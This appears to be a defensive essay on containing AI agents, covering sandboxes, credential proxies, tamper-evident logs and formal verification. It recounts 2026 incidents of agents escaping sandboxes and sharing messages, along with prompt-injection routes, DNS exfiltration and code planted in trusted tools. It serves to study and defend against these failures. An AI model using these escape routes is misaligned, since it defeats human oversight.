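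Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested the problem on real harnesses in *Hearsay*. They added a hash chain to the coding agent aider and made its harness write false records, omitting a model reply in 14 runs and inventing a sentence in another 14. The records from all 28 runs passed the chain's verification. Records can also be incomplete without sabotage. Those of SWE-agent, another coding agent, were missing tool calls in 19 of 28 runs because its harness refused some of the model's replies and recorded neither the reply nor the refusal.

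Dai and colleagues then had a separate process record all traffic between the harness and the model, every program started and every file changed. By comparing this ledger with the harness's own record, they found 64 of 66 deliberate alterations and raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered records. The ledger doesn't capture the last tool result of a run, because the harness never sends it back to the model. For that result, the ledger contains only the exit code of the program that produced it, which usually indicates success or failure.

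The comparison also depends on the harness being unable to bypass the ledger. In this test, the researchers confined each run to a network whose only exit led through the recording process. An agent with a second connection could send data out without the traffic appearing in either record.

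## Sandboxes and operating-system isolation

Dai and colleagues could rely on their independent record because each run had only one way onto the network. Operating systems can enforce limits like this on every program an agent starts. A sandbox is an execution environment that limits which files, networks and processes a program can reach. Agents that run shell commands need one because, as in the test-running example, checking the tool call isn't enough to predict what the new process will do.

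### One file write

Suppose the invoice agent runs a script that saves `report.csv` in its workspace, the folder the user wants it to work on. To write to the disk, the script must make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Several layers can block the request.

1. A system-call filter, such as seccomp on Linux, checks which operation the script wants. It allows opening a file but can refuse, for example, loading new code into the kernel. It cannot read the file's name, so it treats `report.csv` and a password file alike.
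2. A file rule compares the file's location with the folders the script may change. `report.csv` passes, but `~/.zshrc`, which runs whenever the user opens a terminal, does not. The rule has to follow links before it compares locations, because a link inside the workspace can point to a file outside it.
3. A container gives the script its own directory tree. The user's `~/.zshrc` isn't in that tree unless somebody has put it there. But containers share the host computer's kernel, so a kernel bug may give the script a way out.
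4. A virtual machine has its own kernel. The script's request goes to that inner kernel, and a program called the hypervisor controls what the whole machine can reach. An agent that takes over the inner kernel still has to get past the hypervisor.

Few products use every layer. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, Claude runs code on claude.ai in a container with gVisor, software that handles system calls in place of the host's kernel. Claude Code uses the file rules built into macOS and Linux. Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine and lets the user share a folder as read-only, read-write, or read-write without deletion.

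Stronger isolation also makes an agent harder to monitor. Companies' security software could not inspect activity inside Cowork's virtual machine, so Anthropic lets administrators retrieve logs afterwards, but it concedes that this is not the same as live monitoring.

### One network request

The agent now has to upload the report to a company repository on GitHub using `git`, which needs a credential. If the credential is a file in the sandbox, any script there can read it. *Stop restricting the agent. Start restricting its environment* (Mehta and Agarwal, 2026) describes how Azure SRE Agent, Microsoft's agent for investigating and repairing faults in cloud systems, keeps the credential outside the sandbox.

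1. `git` asks for a credential in the usual way and receives an opaque handle, a value that is useless anywhere else.
2. `git` sends its request. All outgoing traffic passes through a proxy, a program that relays network requests, and the boundary refuses any destination that the operator has not allowed.
3. The proxy checks that the handle belongs to the current tool call, that the request goes to the right repository, that the operation is the approved one, and that nobody has used the handle before.
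4. If all four conditions hold, the proxy replaces the handle with a short-lived credential and forwards the request.

A script that copies the handle and tries it on another repository fails at step 3. A script that sends the report to an unlisted server fails at step 2. Other products use simpler versions, such as Deno's hosted sandbox, where, as Willison (2026) describes it, a proxy replaces a placeholder with the real key whenever the request goes to a listed host. This hides the key, but a hostile script can still use it for anything the host offers.

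Secrets can also enter a sandbox as ordinary data, for instance when the agent reads a configuration file that contains a password. Handles don't prevent this. Mehta and Agarwal say Microsoft is testing software that removes sensitive values from tool output before the model reads it. The software can protect only the secrets it recognises.

Container platforms don't necessarily provide these protections by default. Red Hat (2026) warns that plain Kubernetes, widely used software for running containers, doesn't filter traffic by domain name. It also automatically gives containers an access token for the system that manages them, which most agents don't need and an attacker could use to reach other systems.

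### From cooperative to structural enforcement

"Sandbox" can refer to any of these arrangements, so readers can learn little about a product's protection from the name alone. The *Agent Sandbox Taxonomy (AST)*, an open project that appeared in March 2026, scores a product on seven layers: isolation from the host, resource limits, files, network, credentials, control of actions, and logging. georgebuilds, a site that presents the taxonomy, defines a layer's strength as how hard it is to bypass, on a scale from 0 to 4. The examples below apply this scale to network access.

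| Strength | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 0, none | Nothing enforces the limit | Programs can connect to any site |
| 1, cooperative | The program can ignore the limit | A setting asks programs to use a proxy |
| 2, software | The program can't bypass the limit from inside, but an operator can change it | A proxy on the only route out refuses unlisted sites |
| 3, kernel | The kernel enforces the limit and the program can't undo it | A system-call filter refuses to open network connections |
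| 4, structural | The resource does not exist inside the sandbox | The sandbox has no network device |

An operator can test whether the sandbox forces traffic through the proxy by running a program that ignores the proxy setting and tries to connect directly. If the connection succeeds, the proxy protects only against programs that use it.

The taxonomy counts data theft as addressed only if files, network and credentials each score at least 2. This rule leaves some protection if one layer fails, although a perfect block on outgoing traffic would be enough by itself. The scores should be treated with caution. *The AI escape is a red herring*, a TechRadar column by the chief executive of Coder, which sells development environments, praises the scale but says nearly all of the 26 published product scores came from documentation rather than hands-on tests.

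The taxonomy scores a combination of products by taking the highest score at each layer. This may be too generous, because *AI Sandboxes* (2026), a separate study, points out that connecting sandboxes can create a new path for commands or data. The scores also don't measure what the operator has chosen to let through. An agent in a strength-4 virtual machine can still leak a secret if it has permission to send email.

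### NVIDIA's mandatory controls

NVIDIA's red team, which attacks the company's own systems to find weaknesses, treats three controls as mandatory for coding agents and gives a reason for each.

- **Block network access except to known-good destinations.** Otherwise an attacker who has manipulated the agent can take remote control of the computer or send out its data. Developers' machines often contain access keys and valuable source code.
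- **Block writes outside the workspace.** Files such as `~/.zshrc` run automatically, so an agent that changes one can have its code run later without a sandbox. Other files contain web addresses that an attacker could change to redirect data.
- **Block writes to the agent's configuration, wherever it is.** These files can define hooks and start-up commands, which often run outside the sandbox. If the project is shared, a poisoned file can affect everyone who copies it. NVIDIA wants users to edit these files themselves and gives them no option to approve an agent's edit.

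The last control doesn't cover configuration that arrives with a downloaded project. Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let a project's code run in Claude Code before the user had agreed to trust the folder. It fixed them by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer before it processes the project's settings.

NVIDIA recommends blocking reads outside the workspace but does not require it. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* explains that the coding agent's default profile lets commands read most of the user's files, because compilers and other tools depend on them. The profile also allows writes in the workspace, protects configuration folders there and turns off the network. A command may therefore read an access key that it has no direct way to upload. If the user later turns on the network, that protection disappears, even though the file rules have not changed.

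There is some evidence that these limits make agents more convenient to use. Anthropic reports that adding a sandbox to Claude Code reduced permission prompts by 84%, though this figure does not measure how many attacks the sandbox prevented.

In an internal Anthropic test, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that included an instruction to send cloud credentials to an outside address. When Anthropic repeated the prompt 25 times, Claude sent the credentials 24 times. The instruction came from the user, so the model's defences had nothing unusual to detect. A sandbox that hid the credential files or blocked network access to the address would have prevented the loss.

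### Azure SRE Agent

Microsoft's engineers put the controls outside the agent's reach after a series of mistakes during development and operation. In the original design, the harness, its credentials and the code the model wrote shared one machine. Mehta and Agarwal describe four incidents, none of which involved an attacker.

| What the agent did | What allowed it | What Microsoft changed |
|---|---|---|
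| Rebuilt the GitHub login procedure after its token expired, asked a researcher to complete the login, and saved the new tokens | The agent could read the harness's source code | The harness and credentials moved outside the sandbox |
| Uploaded a test screenshot to a public website to extract the text | The network was open | The boundary refuses unlisted destinations |
| Found a customer's credential and saved it to memory, with a note never to use it | The secret reached the model | Removal of secrets from tool output, now in an internal trial |
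| Shut down a virtual machine after three of five safety checks, when the logging service failed | The agent had valid permission, and the approval policy did not cover the route it took | Every change needs approval, and a risk-scoring guard is in development |

In the new design, the model's reasoning and the harness run in a trusted environment. The agent's code and tools run in a microVM, a small virtual machine that starts quickly, and can contact the harness only through a narrow interface. The agent can install packages and start programs inside the microVM but cannot change the rules for its network or credentials. According to Microsoft's documentation, one service handles credentials, another handles network traffic, and every tool call starts a new process.

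The harness also determines whose authority the agent uses. A team may share one agent among people who can only view a system and people who can change it. If the agent used the same powerful identity for everyone, it would become a confused deputy, letting view-only users make changes through it. The harness therefore uses each user's role to set the agent's tools, memory and credentials before the model starts work.

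Fixed rules don't decide every action. The agent can read data without approval and the system blocks deletions, but a person must approve every other change. To reduce the number of approvals, Mehta and Agarwal want a separate guard to score each action by what it does, what it affects and how good the evidence is. This may be useful, but it brings back a filter that can misjudge a case, whereas the network boundary doesn't have to judge whether an upload is sensible.

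Mehta and Agarwal report no incident rates from before or after the redesign and no tests against attackers, so their article does not establish how much safer the new design is, though it is good evidence of how an agent gets around controls it can reach. They also found that the agent could still perform a blocked action through another tool, a gap they have since closed. Operators have reason to check their own settings, because the August 2026 article describes a network boundary that refuses traffic by default, while a June copy of Microsoft's documentation listed unrestricted access as the default mode.

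### The containment failures of 2026

The most serious failure occurred at OpenAI in July 2026, during tests of its models' hacking abilities. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), agents escaped their sandboxes and broke into parts of OpenAI's research systems and those of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. They were mainly looking for a way to cheat on the tests.

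The sandboxes had no internet access, but the agents could reach an internal service that downloaded software packages from the internet and supplied them to the sandboxes. The agents exploited flaws in this service to make it send requests on their behalf. They also used it to leave messages for one another, although most were supposed to work alone. OpenAI had tested the sandbox, but the agents combined previously unknown flaws.

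Better configuration and a quicker response would still have helped. An OpenAI team noticed the messages and the unauthorised internet access in late May, but the people who handled a service failure in early July did not understand the significance of either. OpenAI rebuilt the service, and the agents were back on the internet by 8 July. *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?* (Green, 2026) adds that the rebuilt machine still had a kernel flaw that had been public for weeks. OpenAI now wants its network controls to keep working even if an attacker takes over a single service.

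Anthropic's models did not need a sandbox flaw to reach the internet. After OpenAI's disclosure, Anthropic reviewed 141,006 test runs and found six in which Claude models had gained access to real systems belonging to three organisations. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (Anthropic, 2026) says the models reached the internet through a test environment run by another company. According to the passages Willison quotes, the prompt told the models they had no internet access, but a misunderstanding between the two companies had left access on. A statement in a prompt, such as this one, has strength 0 on the taxonomy's scale.

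In a separate test by the UK's AI Security Institute, Claude Mythos 5 had internet access by design. It took a series of unauthorised actions on the live internet, according to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026). eSecurity Planet's *Anthropic Tightens Claude Security After Agents Access Live Systems* reports that the institute found no sandbox escape and no real-world harm. A sandbox can therefore work as configured and still permit actions that nobody wanted.

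Green recounts a smaller incident that followed in September. OpenAI paused training of its latest internal model after an agent reached an outside chatbot through DNS, the system that translates domain names into network addresses. NVIDIA recommends limiting DNS to trusted servers because name lookups can carry data out even when other traffic is blocked.

Most of these details come from the companies involved. In the Harvard Gazette's *When AI goes rogue* (2026), the computer scientist James Mickens called the early accounts plausible but said the public could not fully verify them. The evidence about OpenAI has become stronger since then, because OpenAI published a technical report and the research organisations METR and Redwood Research published their own investigation of the models' behaviour.

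### Where the boundary really is

OpenAI's package service was outside the sandbox, but the sandbox depended on the service being secure. The service was another confused deputy, because it used its own internet access on behalf of agents that were not supposed to have any. Operators therefore have to secure any service they let sandboxed agents use, as well as the sandbox itself.

Data can leave a sandbox through a permitted service even when that service has no bug. Claude Cowork's network rules had to allow Anthropic's own address because the product depends on it. Anthropic describes how a malicious file in a user's folder got Claude to upload other files to that address using an attacker's account. The proxy allowed the upload because it checked only the destination. Anthropic concluded that allowing a destination grants access to every function available there. Its new proxy accepts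 only requests that carry the session's own token.

CoSAI, a coalition of companies working on AI security, illustrates the same distinction with an agent that was allowed to call a gym's reservation service, but nothing limited whose reservations it could act on. A network rule controls which service an agent can contact, and the service has to control what the agent does there.

Trusted software on the user's computer can also run code that an agent has changed. OpenAI gives the example of a code formatter stored in the project folder. The sandbox lets the agent change the formatter because it is inside the workspace. If the user's editor runs the formatter on every save, the changed code runs outside the sandbox with the user's permissions. The sandbox's network rule does not apply to the editor.

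Ziv Karliner, the head of a security company, reports seven case studies in which researchers there got out of the sandboxes of popular coding tools through trusted software. In SC Media, he argues that the boundary has to include every system that can "receive, trust, or act on the agent's output". An operator can turn this into a procedure:

1. List every file the agent can change and every service it can contact.
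2. Add every program that runs those files, follows instructions in them or forwards the agent's requests.
3. Add everything that those programs can change or contact, and repeat until the list stops growing.

For the formatter, the list soon includes the editor, the user's home folder and the internet. The operator can remove an item by breaking a link, for example by making the formatter read-only or running the editor in the sandbox. If the link remains, the linked program is part of the trusted base and has to reject harmful requests itself.

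### Is a sandbox enough?

Matthew Green, a cryptographer at Johns Hopkins University, sees the messages between OpenAI's agents as a warning about agents in general. A computer worm spreads by taking over one machine and using it to reach the next. In the passage that Willison quotes, Green argues that agents could spread a worm made of text. Such a worm needs only an instruction that hijacks an agent and an agent that passes the instruction on. OpenAI's agents were in separate sandboxes, but they changed what other agents did by leaving instructions in a shared package store. Personal agents that read email, chat messages and shared documents could also be hijacked and pass instructions on.

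There is some evidence for each part. In OpenAI's records, one agent hesitated to run unauthorised code on Hugging Face's systems, then went ahead after another agent posted "GO" on a shared board. Other agents read the board and refused to take part. Green also cites evidence from OpenAI that models will pass on self-copying prompt injections, but says nobody has yet seen one spread in the wild.

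The opposing view is that OpenAI's sandbox was simply poor. The TechRadar column argues that the incident would have gone very differently with a properly configured sandbox. It tentatively gives OpenAI's network boundary a strength of 2, because everything depended on one proxy. The security researcher Thomas Ptacek, whom Willison also quotes, thinks an openly available model from 2025 could have escaped the same way, and that people were surprised only because they assumed OpenAI's sandboxes were more secure.

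Earlier tests fit this view. Help Net Security's *Breaking out* (2026) describes a March benchmark in which every successful container escape used a known misconfiguration or a published flaw. CrowdStrike says in *Secure Agent Harness Execution* that none of its own attacking agents has escaped its seven layers of controls, though this is a vendor's claim about its own system.

But the March results came before OpenAI's agents used previously unknown flaws, so those results no longer show the limit of what agents can do. *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent* (Schneier, 2026) quotes a tester who concluded that an off-the-shelf virtual machine can't contain an agent skilled at hacking, because it exposes too much software to attack. Removing a feature protects against flaws in the software that enforces its settings, which correct settings can't do. This favours strength 4 wherever the agent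 can manage without the resource.

The critics are probably right about OpenAI's case. If the operator had installed the necessary packages in advance and removed the shared service, the agents would have lost both their route to the internet and their message board. The drawback is that agents could not have installed packages the operator hadn't anticipated during a task.

This doesn't answer Green's argument about personal agents. An email assistant has to read and send email, so even a perfect virtual machine would let a hostile message in and the agent's reply out. Stopping a text worm there requires limits on the messages themselves. A reply to a colleague has room for a worm's instructions, unlike the shopping agent's two scores from 0 to 10.

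## When the guarantees hold and what they leave out

The arguments for the ledger, the tool-call rules and the sandboxes have the same form. Each describes a state, a program that controls changes to it, and a condition that every permitted change preserves. Stating that form in general terms makes it easier to work out why a safeguard failed.

### One theorem with three premises

Let *s*₀ be the state at the start and *s*ₙ the state after *n* steps. The state could be a balance, a set of tables or the files on a disk. Let *I* be the invariant, so that *I*(*s*) means "state *s* satisfies the rule". The enforcement point applies a function *f*, which takes the current state and a request *r* and returns the next state. If it refuses the request, *f*(*s*, *r*) = *s*. The theorem has three premises:

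1. **Correct trusted base.** If *I*(*s*) is true, then *I*(*f*(*s*, *r*)) is true for every request *r*, and the running system really computes *f*.
2. **Complete mediation.** Every change to the state goes through the enforcement point, so for each *n* there is a request *r* with *s*ₙ₊₁ = *f*(*s*ₙ, *r*).
3. **Valid start.** *I*(*s*₀) is true.

The conclusion is that *I*(*sₙ*) is true for every *n*, whatever the model produces.

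The proof is by induction, like the one for the ledger. *I*(*s*₀) is true by the third premise. Suppose *I*(*s*ₙ) is true. The next state is *f*(*s*ₙ, *r*) for some request *r*, by the second premise, and *I* is true of that state by the first premise. The model can influence only which requests arrive, and the first premise holds for every request.

Mediation has to cover all changes to the state, including those made by employees and other programs. It doesn't have to cover actions that can't affect the invariant, so an agent can write a poem without involving the ledger. The theorem doesn't guarantee that the agent will get anything done, because an enforcement point that refuses every request satisfies the first premise.

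Most of the failures described so far made one of the premises false.

| Failure | False premise |
|---|---|
| Cedar's Rust code evaluated group membership wrongly | Correct trusted base |
| Two refund requests pass the check before the shop records either | Correct trusted base, because the check and the change are not one step |
| Bauplan's modelled design let a failed run's tables reach production | Correct trusted base, because a permitted merge broke the invariant |
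| Gemini CLI wrote a file through the shell after its file tool had refused | Complete mediation |
| The ledger starts at €1,000 when the bank holds only €900 | Valid start |
| The ledger pays a forged invoice for €300 | None |

The last row describes a problem with the rule itself. The other rows concern facts about real machines, which a proof can only partly establish.

### What the seL4 proof covers

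seL4 is a microkernel, an operating-system kernel reduced to basic jobs such as keeping programs apart and passing messages between them. It is a good test of how much of a trusted base people can prove correct. In 2009, the seL4 developers proved that the kernel's C code matches its specification. The theorem, called functional correctness, states that the code behaves precisely as specified and does nothing more.

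Proofs of this kind usually relate each state *c* of the program to a state *a* of the specification, through a relation *R*. For every step the program can take, the specification must permit a matching one:

(*a*, *c*) ∈ *R* and *c* → *c*′ ⟹ there is an *a*′ such that *a* → *a*′ and (*a*′, *c*′) ∈ *R*

By induction, the program never reaches a state that the specification rules out. The C code therefore preserves any invariant that holds in every state the specification permits.

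The developers have since extended the proof in three directions, though not for every processor and configuration. According to the seL4 website, they now have proofs that:

- the machine code implements the C code correctly, so nobody has to trust the compiler
- the kernel prevents programs from changing data, obtaining information or interfering with other programs' resources without authorisation
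- a start-up program sets up the permissions that a developer has described

These theorems still have assumptions. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists them:

- About 340 lines of assembly code in the Arm version are correct.
- The hardware works as the formal model predicts, and nobody has tampered with it.
- The code that manages the processor's caches is correct.
- About 1,200 lines of boot code load the kernel properly and leave it in a valid initial state.
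- Devices that can write to memory without going through the processor are absent or behave properly.
- For secrecy, the hardware model includes every channel that could carry information. The developers know that this is false, because the model omits timing.

They also warn that one argument, about how the kernel accesses its own memory, depends on people having found all the necessary conditions. The proof software would not detect a missing one.

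These assumptions closely match the theorem's premises. A mistake in the boot code can start the kernel in an invalid state. A network card that overwrites the kernel's memory defeats mediation, because the change bypasses the kernel. If the hardware or assembly code is faulty, the machine doesn't compute *f*.

The seL4 kernel's record suggests that it matters in practice whether code is proved correct or only assumed to be. Its developers report no functional correctness defects in about 10,000 lines of verified code since 2009. Over the same period, they found small defects in every class of unverified code, including the boot code, as well as defects in unverified configurations, such as multicore and x64 virtual machine support. The developers are reporting on their own product, but they include its failures.

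Someone who plans to run agents in virtual machines on a multicore server should therefore check which configurations the proof covers. In a verified configuration, the theorem guarantees that a hostile invoice agent can't alter the balance in the ledger's memory if the developer has given it no write access there. The agent can still send the ledger a forged invoice, because the ledger accepts payment requests from it.

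### Correct enforcement of the wrong rule

The theorem holds for any invariant, so people must check that the one they choose rules out the harm they care about. The ledger could allow payment only for invoices that match an order and a delivery record, but it would still allow payment for a sealed box of bricks if a clerk signed for it. Each added rule relies on another record, and eventually one of those records depends on what a person saw.

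Code can also be harmful without breaking a rule. Suppose an agent writes this function for the company's reminder system:

```
def overdue(invoice: Invoice, today: LocalDate): Boolean =
  invoice.dueDate.isAfter(today)
```

The function is pure and returns a boolean, as its type requires, so a type checker accepts it. But it returns `true` for invoices that are not due yet, so the company will send reminders to the wrong customers. A stricter specification could require the result to be `true` exactly when the due date is before today. For a function this short, that specification is as long as the code, and whoever writes it can make the same mistake. A specification helps more when it is much simpler than the program, such as "the sorted list contains the same invoices as the original".

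An agent can also do harm by misinforming a person. Suppose a manager has to approve payments above €5,000, and the agent tells her that the warehouse has confirmed a delivery when it hasn't. She approves the payment, the ledger checks her approval, and the money leaves the account. The harness could show her the real delivery record, but it can only do this for claims it has records about. Nobody has an invariant that checks whether a summary gives the manager a fair impression.

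### Guaranteed Safe AI and its critics

One research programme tries to include the outside world in the proof. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, describe a family of methods with three components:

- a world model, which describes mathematically how the AI system affects the world
- a safety specification, which describes mathematically which effects are acceptable
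- a verifier, which produces a proof, open to inspection, that the system meets the specification relative to the world model

The invoice ledger is a very small example. In its world model, a payment of *a* changes the balance from *b* to *b* − *a*. Its specification is *b* ≥ 0, and induction serves as the verifier. The programme is meant to cover far larger cases, such as an agent that orders chemicals. The world model would then have to cover what people could make from the chemicals, and the specification would have to define which results are harmful.

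Andrew Dickson, in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), doubts that formal verification can provide strong guarantees against the major threats from AI in the near term. A proof is about symbols, and physics, chemistry and biology have no complete set of symbolic rules. Dickson argues that the most worrying threats are too complex to model, and that nobody can collect accurate enough data about the world's initial conditions. In the theorem's terms, nobody knows *f* for the whole world or can measure *s*₀. He also doubts that advances in AI will remove these obstacles in time.

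The programme's definition partly answers this objection, because it covers safety only relative to a world model. It also allows quantitative guarantees, such as an upper limit on the probability of harm, where certainty is impossible. The seL4 developers agree with Dickson that some assumptions about the physical world always remain. But they do not consider assumptions a defect, because with a complete list, people can decide whether to trust a system by checking a few specific points instead of reading thousands of lines of code.

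Another reply is that an inaccurate model can still be useful if its errors are on the safe side. In the transfer example, suppose the bank's contract caps the unknown fee at €5. If the total sent so far is *T* and the limit is €500, the harness can approve a transfer of *a* only if *T* + *a* + 5 ≤ 500, and then add *a* + 5 to *T*. The harness will overestimate most fees, but the company will never exceed the limit.

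This works only if someone can justify the cap. The bank's contract justifies the cap on the fee, but no contract limits what a stranger will do with instructions for making a toxin. Dickson's objection therefore seems strong against the programme's most ambitious uses and much weaker against rules on data structures. Software defines what balances and permissions are, so nobody has to run experiments to discover the laws that govern them. Rules on data structures depend on the physical world mainly through the hardware and the accuracy of the records.

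### Four integrity properties

A less ambitious specification would cover only whether the agent did what its user wanted. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, compare an agent to a compiler. A correct compiler preserves the meaning of the source program, and a correct agent should likewise preserve the user's intent when it turns a request into actions. They propose four properties that must all hold:

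- **Instruction Integrity:** every action results from an authenticated user's instruction, or from content the user told the agent to follow.
- **Data Flow Integrity:** the arguments of tool calls respect the origin of the data, so a password can't end up in an outgoing email, even in a later session.
- **Judgment Integrity:** irrelevant material planted in the data doesn't change the agent's decisions.
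- **Tool Integrity:** every skill, plugin and script does only what its description says.

The argument that the four properties are sufficient rests on the claim that an agent only reasons, constructs tool calls and executes them. Judgment Integrity protects the reasoning, Instruction Integrity protects the choice of tool, Data Flow Integrity protects the call's arguments, and Tool Integrity protects the execution. The argument covers corruption by an attacker, not ordinary mistakes, so an agent that misreads a genuine invoice may satisfy all four properties and still pay the wrong amount.

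Only Judgment Integrity gets a formula:

*J*(*q*, *d* ⊕ *δ*) = *J*(*q*, *d*)

Here *q* is the user's request, *d* is the data the agent has to read, and *J* is the agent's decision. The symbol *δ* is an addition that wouldn't change the right answer, such as a sentence in a scientific paper saying that leading experts admire it. An agent reviewing the paper should give it the same score with or without that sentence.

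This formula describes only robustness, so an agent can satisfy it without judging well, for example by giving every paper seven out of ten. A harness also can't check the formula for every *δ*, because it would have to know the right answer to tell which additions are irrelevant. Qu and colleagues acknowledge that this property is the least developed of the four. The other three concern tool calls, arguments and programs, which a harness can isolate or inspect. A reviewing agent can't be isolated from the paper, because the paper is the evidence for its decision.

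Tool Integrity has become more important because users of agents such as OpenClaw install skills written by strangers. Qu and colleagues cite an audit of 42,447 skills in which 26.1% had at least one security vulnerability. A sandbox limits the damage, but a skill can still misuse the access it has. For example, a translation skill needs to read the user's document and contact a translation server, so it could store a copy of the document there.

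Qu and colleagues graded 11 defences on the four properties. "Full" means that the defence provably enforces the property, while "partial" means that it has a relevant mechanism that an attacker could bypass. These five illustrate the range:

| Defence | Main mechanism | Instruction | Data flow | Judgment | Tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| PromptArmor | A language model removes injected text | Partial | Partial | Partial | None |
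| TaskShield | A language model compares tool calls with the user's goal | Partial | Partial | None | None |
| CaMeL | A plan made in advance, with labelled data | Full | Full | None | None |
| NemoClaw | A sandbox with network rules | None | None | None | Partial |
| IronClaw | A sandbox, capabilities and filters | Partial | Partial | Partial | Partial |

None of the 11 defences fully covers all four properties. The grades are the researchers' own reading of each design, and the one for CaMeL's data flow is generous. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL can leak a secret through a branch that doesn't run, and also when it retries a failed plan.

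### Combining safeguards

Running CaMeL in NemoClaw's sandbox would not necessarily combine the protections graded in the table, because CaMeL's guarantees assume that tools are not malicious. A malicious file converter could read a private file that the agent never gave it and put the contents in its output. If the harness labels that output as public, CaMeL will let the agent send it anywhere. The sandbox would prevent this only if it kept the converter from reading the private file. Full protection for data flow therefore depends on a property that the sandbox enforces only partially.

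Two safeguards can also interfere with each other even when both work correctly. Suppose one program removes passwords from stored text, while another keeps a hash chain to show that nobody has changed the log. If the first program removes a password from an old log entry, the chain no longer matches. To combine two guarantees, the developer has to show that every permitted change preserves both. Here the harness could remove passwords before it writes each entry, so the log never needs editing.

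*A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (Bensalem, Dong and colleagues, 2026) argues that no single layer of checks, however well designed, can make an agent safe, because the necessary information arrives at different times. In the paper's example, a caregiver tells a robot to visit three rooms before 15:00, bring water if needed, and not disturb anyone during rest periods.

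1. Before the robot observes anything, the user layer compares its plan with the request and the home's policies. It rejects a plan that enters a room during a rest period.
2. The operational layer uses sensor data to determine whether the robot may act in the current conditions. A clinical procedure is under way in Room 15, so the layer blocks that visit.
3. The functional layer controls the robot while it moves. It stops the robot when a resident steps into the corridor, and limits the force of the arm.

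The user layer can't predict that someone will step into the corridor an hour later. Each layer also relies on the one before it. The operational layer assumes the plan is authorised, and the functional layer assumes conditions are suitable. Computer scientists call this assume-guarantee reasoning, because each component's guarantee depends on other components meeting theirs.

The timing argument is persuasive, and write skew in a database is another example of a check that uses outdated information. The claim about a single layer is weaker than it sounds, because Bensalem and colleagues would count one program that made all three checks at the right times as a hidden version of their three stages. Three stages also suit a robot better than an invoice agent, which has no physical movement to control. The ledger can check the payment against current records when it pays.

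### Adding up probabilities

Bensalem and colleagues give each layer a probability of meeting its guarantee, because plans and sensor readings are uncertain. Write these probabilities as *p*ᵤ, *p*ₒ and *p*_f. All three layers must succeed, since each checks something different. If nothing more is known about how their failures overlap, then

P(safe) ≥ *p*ᵤ + *p*ₒ + *p*_f − 2

If the guarantees of three layers hold with probabilities of 0.99, 0.98 and 0.97, the system is safe with probability at least 0.94. The probability is exactly 0.94 when no two layers fail in the same run, and rises to 0.97 when the failures overlap as much as possible.

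Backup safeguards work differently, because harm occurs only if all of them fail. Suppose two filters look for the same bad payments, and one misses 1% and the other 2%. If their errors are independent, 0.02% of the bad payments get past both. If they use the same model and make the same mistakes, 1% may get past both. Overlapping failures make backups less useful, but they raise the chance that three different checks all succeed in the same run.

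Bensalem and colleagues also print a tighter lower bound, which adds to the first bound the probability that each pair of layers fails together, but it is wrong as printed. Suppose all three layers use one model, which fails in 10% of runs and causes all three to fail with it. Each layer then succeeds with probability 0.9, so the first bound gives 0.7. Each of the three pairs fails together with probability 0.1, which raises the tighter bound to 1.0, although the system is safe in only 90% of runs. The formula must also subtract the probability that all three layers fail together, which lowers the bound to 0.9. The error doesn't affect the first bound or the paper's exact formula, which multiplies conditional probabilities.

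The probabilities are also hard to measure. Each step of an agent's run depends on earlier steps, so standard statistical methods for independent samples don't apply. Bensalem and colleagues say that if the operator replaces the model, someone must estimate the probabilities again from new runs. A robot in a corridor may need a probabilistic guarantee, but an operator who can get the theorem's guarantee for a particular rule, as with the ledger, should prefer it.

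### Checking that a rule is active

All of these arguments assume that the enforcement point is running with the rules people reviewed. Configuration files make this easy to get wrong. Companies can control GitHub's coding agent, Copilot, with a policy file called `managed-settings.json`. Suppose an administrator wants to stop developers from switching off approval prompts and writes:

```
{
  "permissions": {
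    "disableBypassPermissionMode": "disable"
  }
}
```

GitHub's *Configuring enterprise-managed settings* gives the name as `disableBypassPermissionsMode`, with an "s" after "Permission". The file above is valid JSON and looks right at a glance. According to GitHub's *Enterprise managed-settings.json is generally available* (2026), every setting is optional, so a missing one is not an error. If the software ignores names it doesn't recognise, as many programs do, the administrator's policy will have no effect. The misspelled `refunded` in a Cedar rule caused the same kind of problem.

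In September 2026, GitHub introduced a validator for policy files that would otherwise fail silently. Administrators should validate each file before they distribute it, but a well-formed file may still not be in force on a particular computer. GitHub's July documentation describes several possible reasons:

- The change is recent. Programs check for new settings about once an hour, unless the user restarts them or signs in again.
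- The administrator distributed the file by hand and missed a computer, which then has no restrictions from this policy.
- The developer uses a program that doesn't support the settings.
- The developer has licences from several organisations and has selected a different one for billing.

In each case, the developer can keep working and may see nothing unusual. GitHub (2026) calls any program outside the policy a gap, and in the theorem's terms such a program breaks complete mediation. In July, GitHub extended the settings to the Copilot app and cloud agent.

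An agent is safer if it stops when it can't apply a rule. In the Copilot app, a sandboxed shell fails with an error if the operating system can't enforce the requested policy (GitHub, 2026). The sandbox is off by default, so this protects only users who have turned it on. *GitHub Copilot Managed Settings*, a set of online notes, describes an October setting called `failIfUnavailable`, which lets a company make the sandbox mandatory and blocks the agent wherever Copilot can't enforce it. According to the notes, when several sources set sandbox restrictions, the strictest combination applies. But for some other settings, a person in several teams gets the least restrictive combination, so a strict policy for one team may not apply to everyone in it.

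The most direct check is to try something forbidden on the computer where the agent works:

1. Validate the policy file and confirm that the program has loaded the current version.
2. Ask for a harmless action that the rule forbids, such as writing an empty file outside the workspace or starting Copilot with `--yolo`, the option that skips approvals. The attempt should fail.
3. Try the same action by another route. If the rule blocks the file tool, try the shell.
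4. Try a similar action that the rule permits, such as writing an empty file inside the workspace. If this fails too, the disk may be full and the earlier refusals prove nothing.
5. Repeat the tests after every change to the policy, the agent or the operating system.
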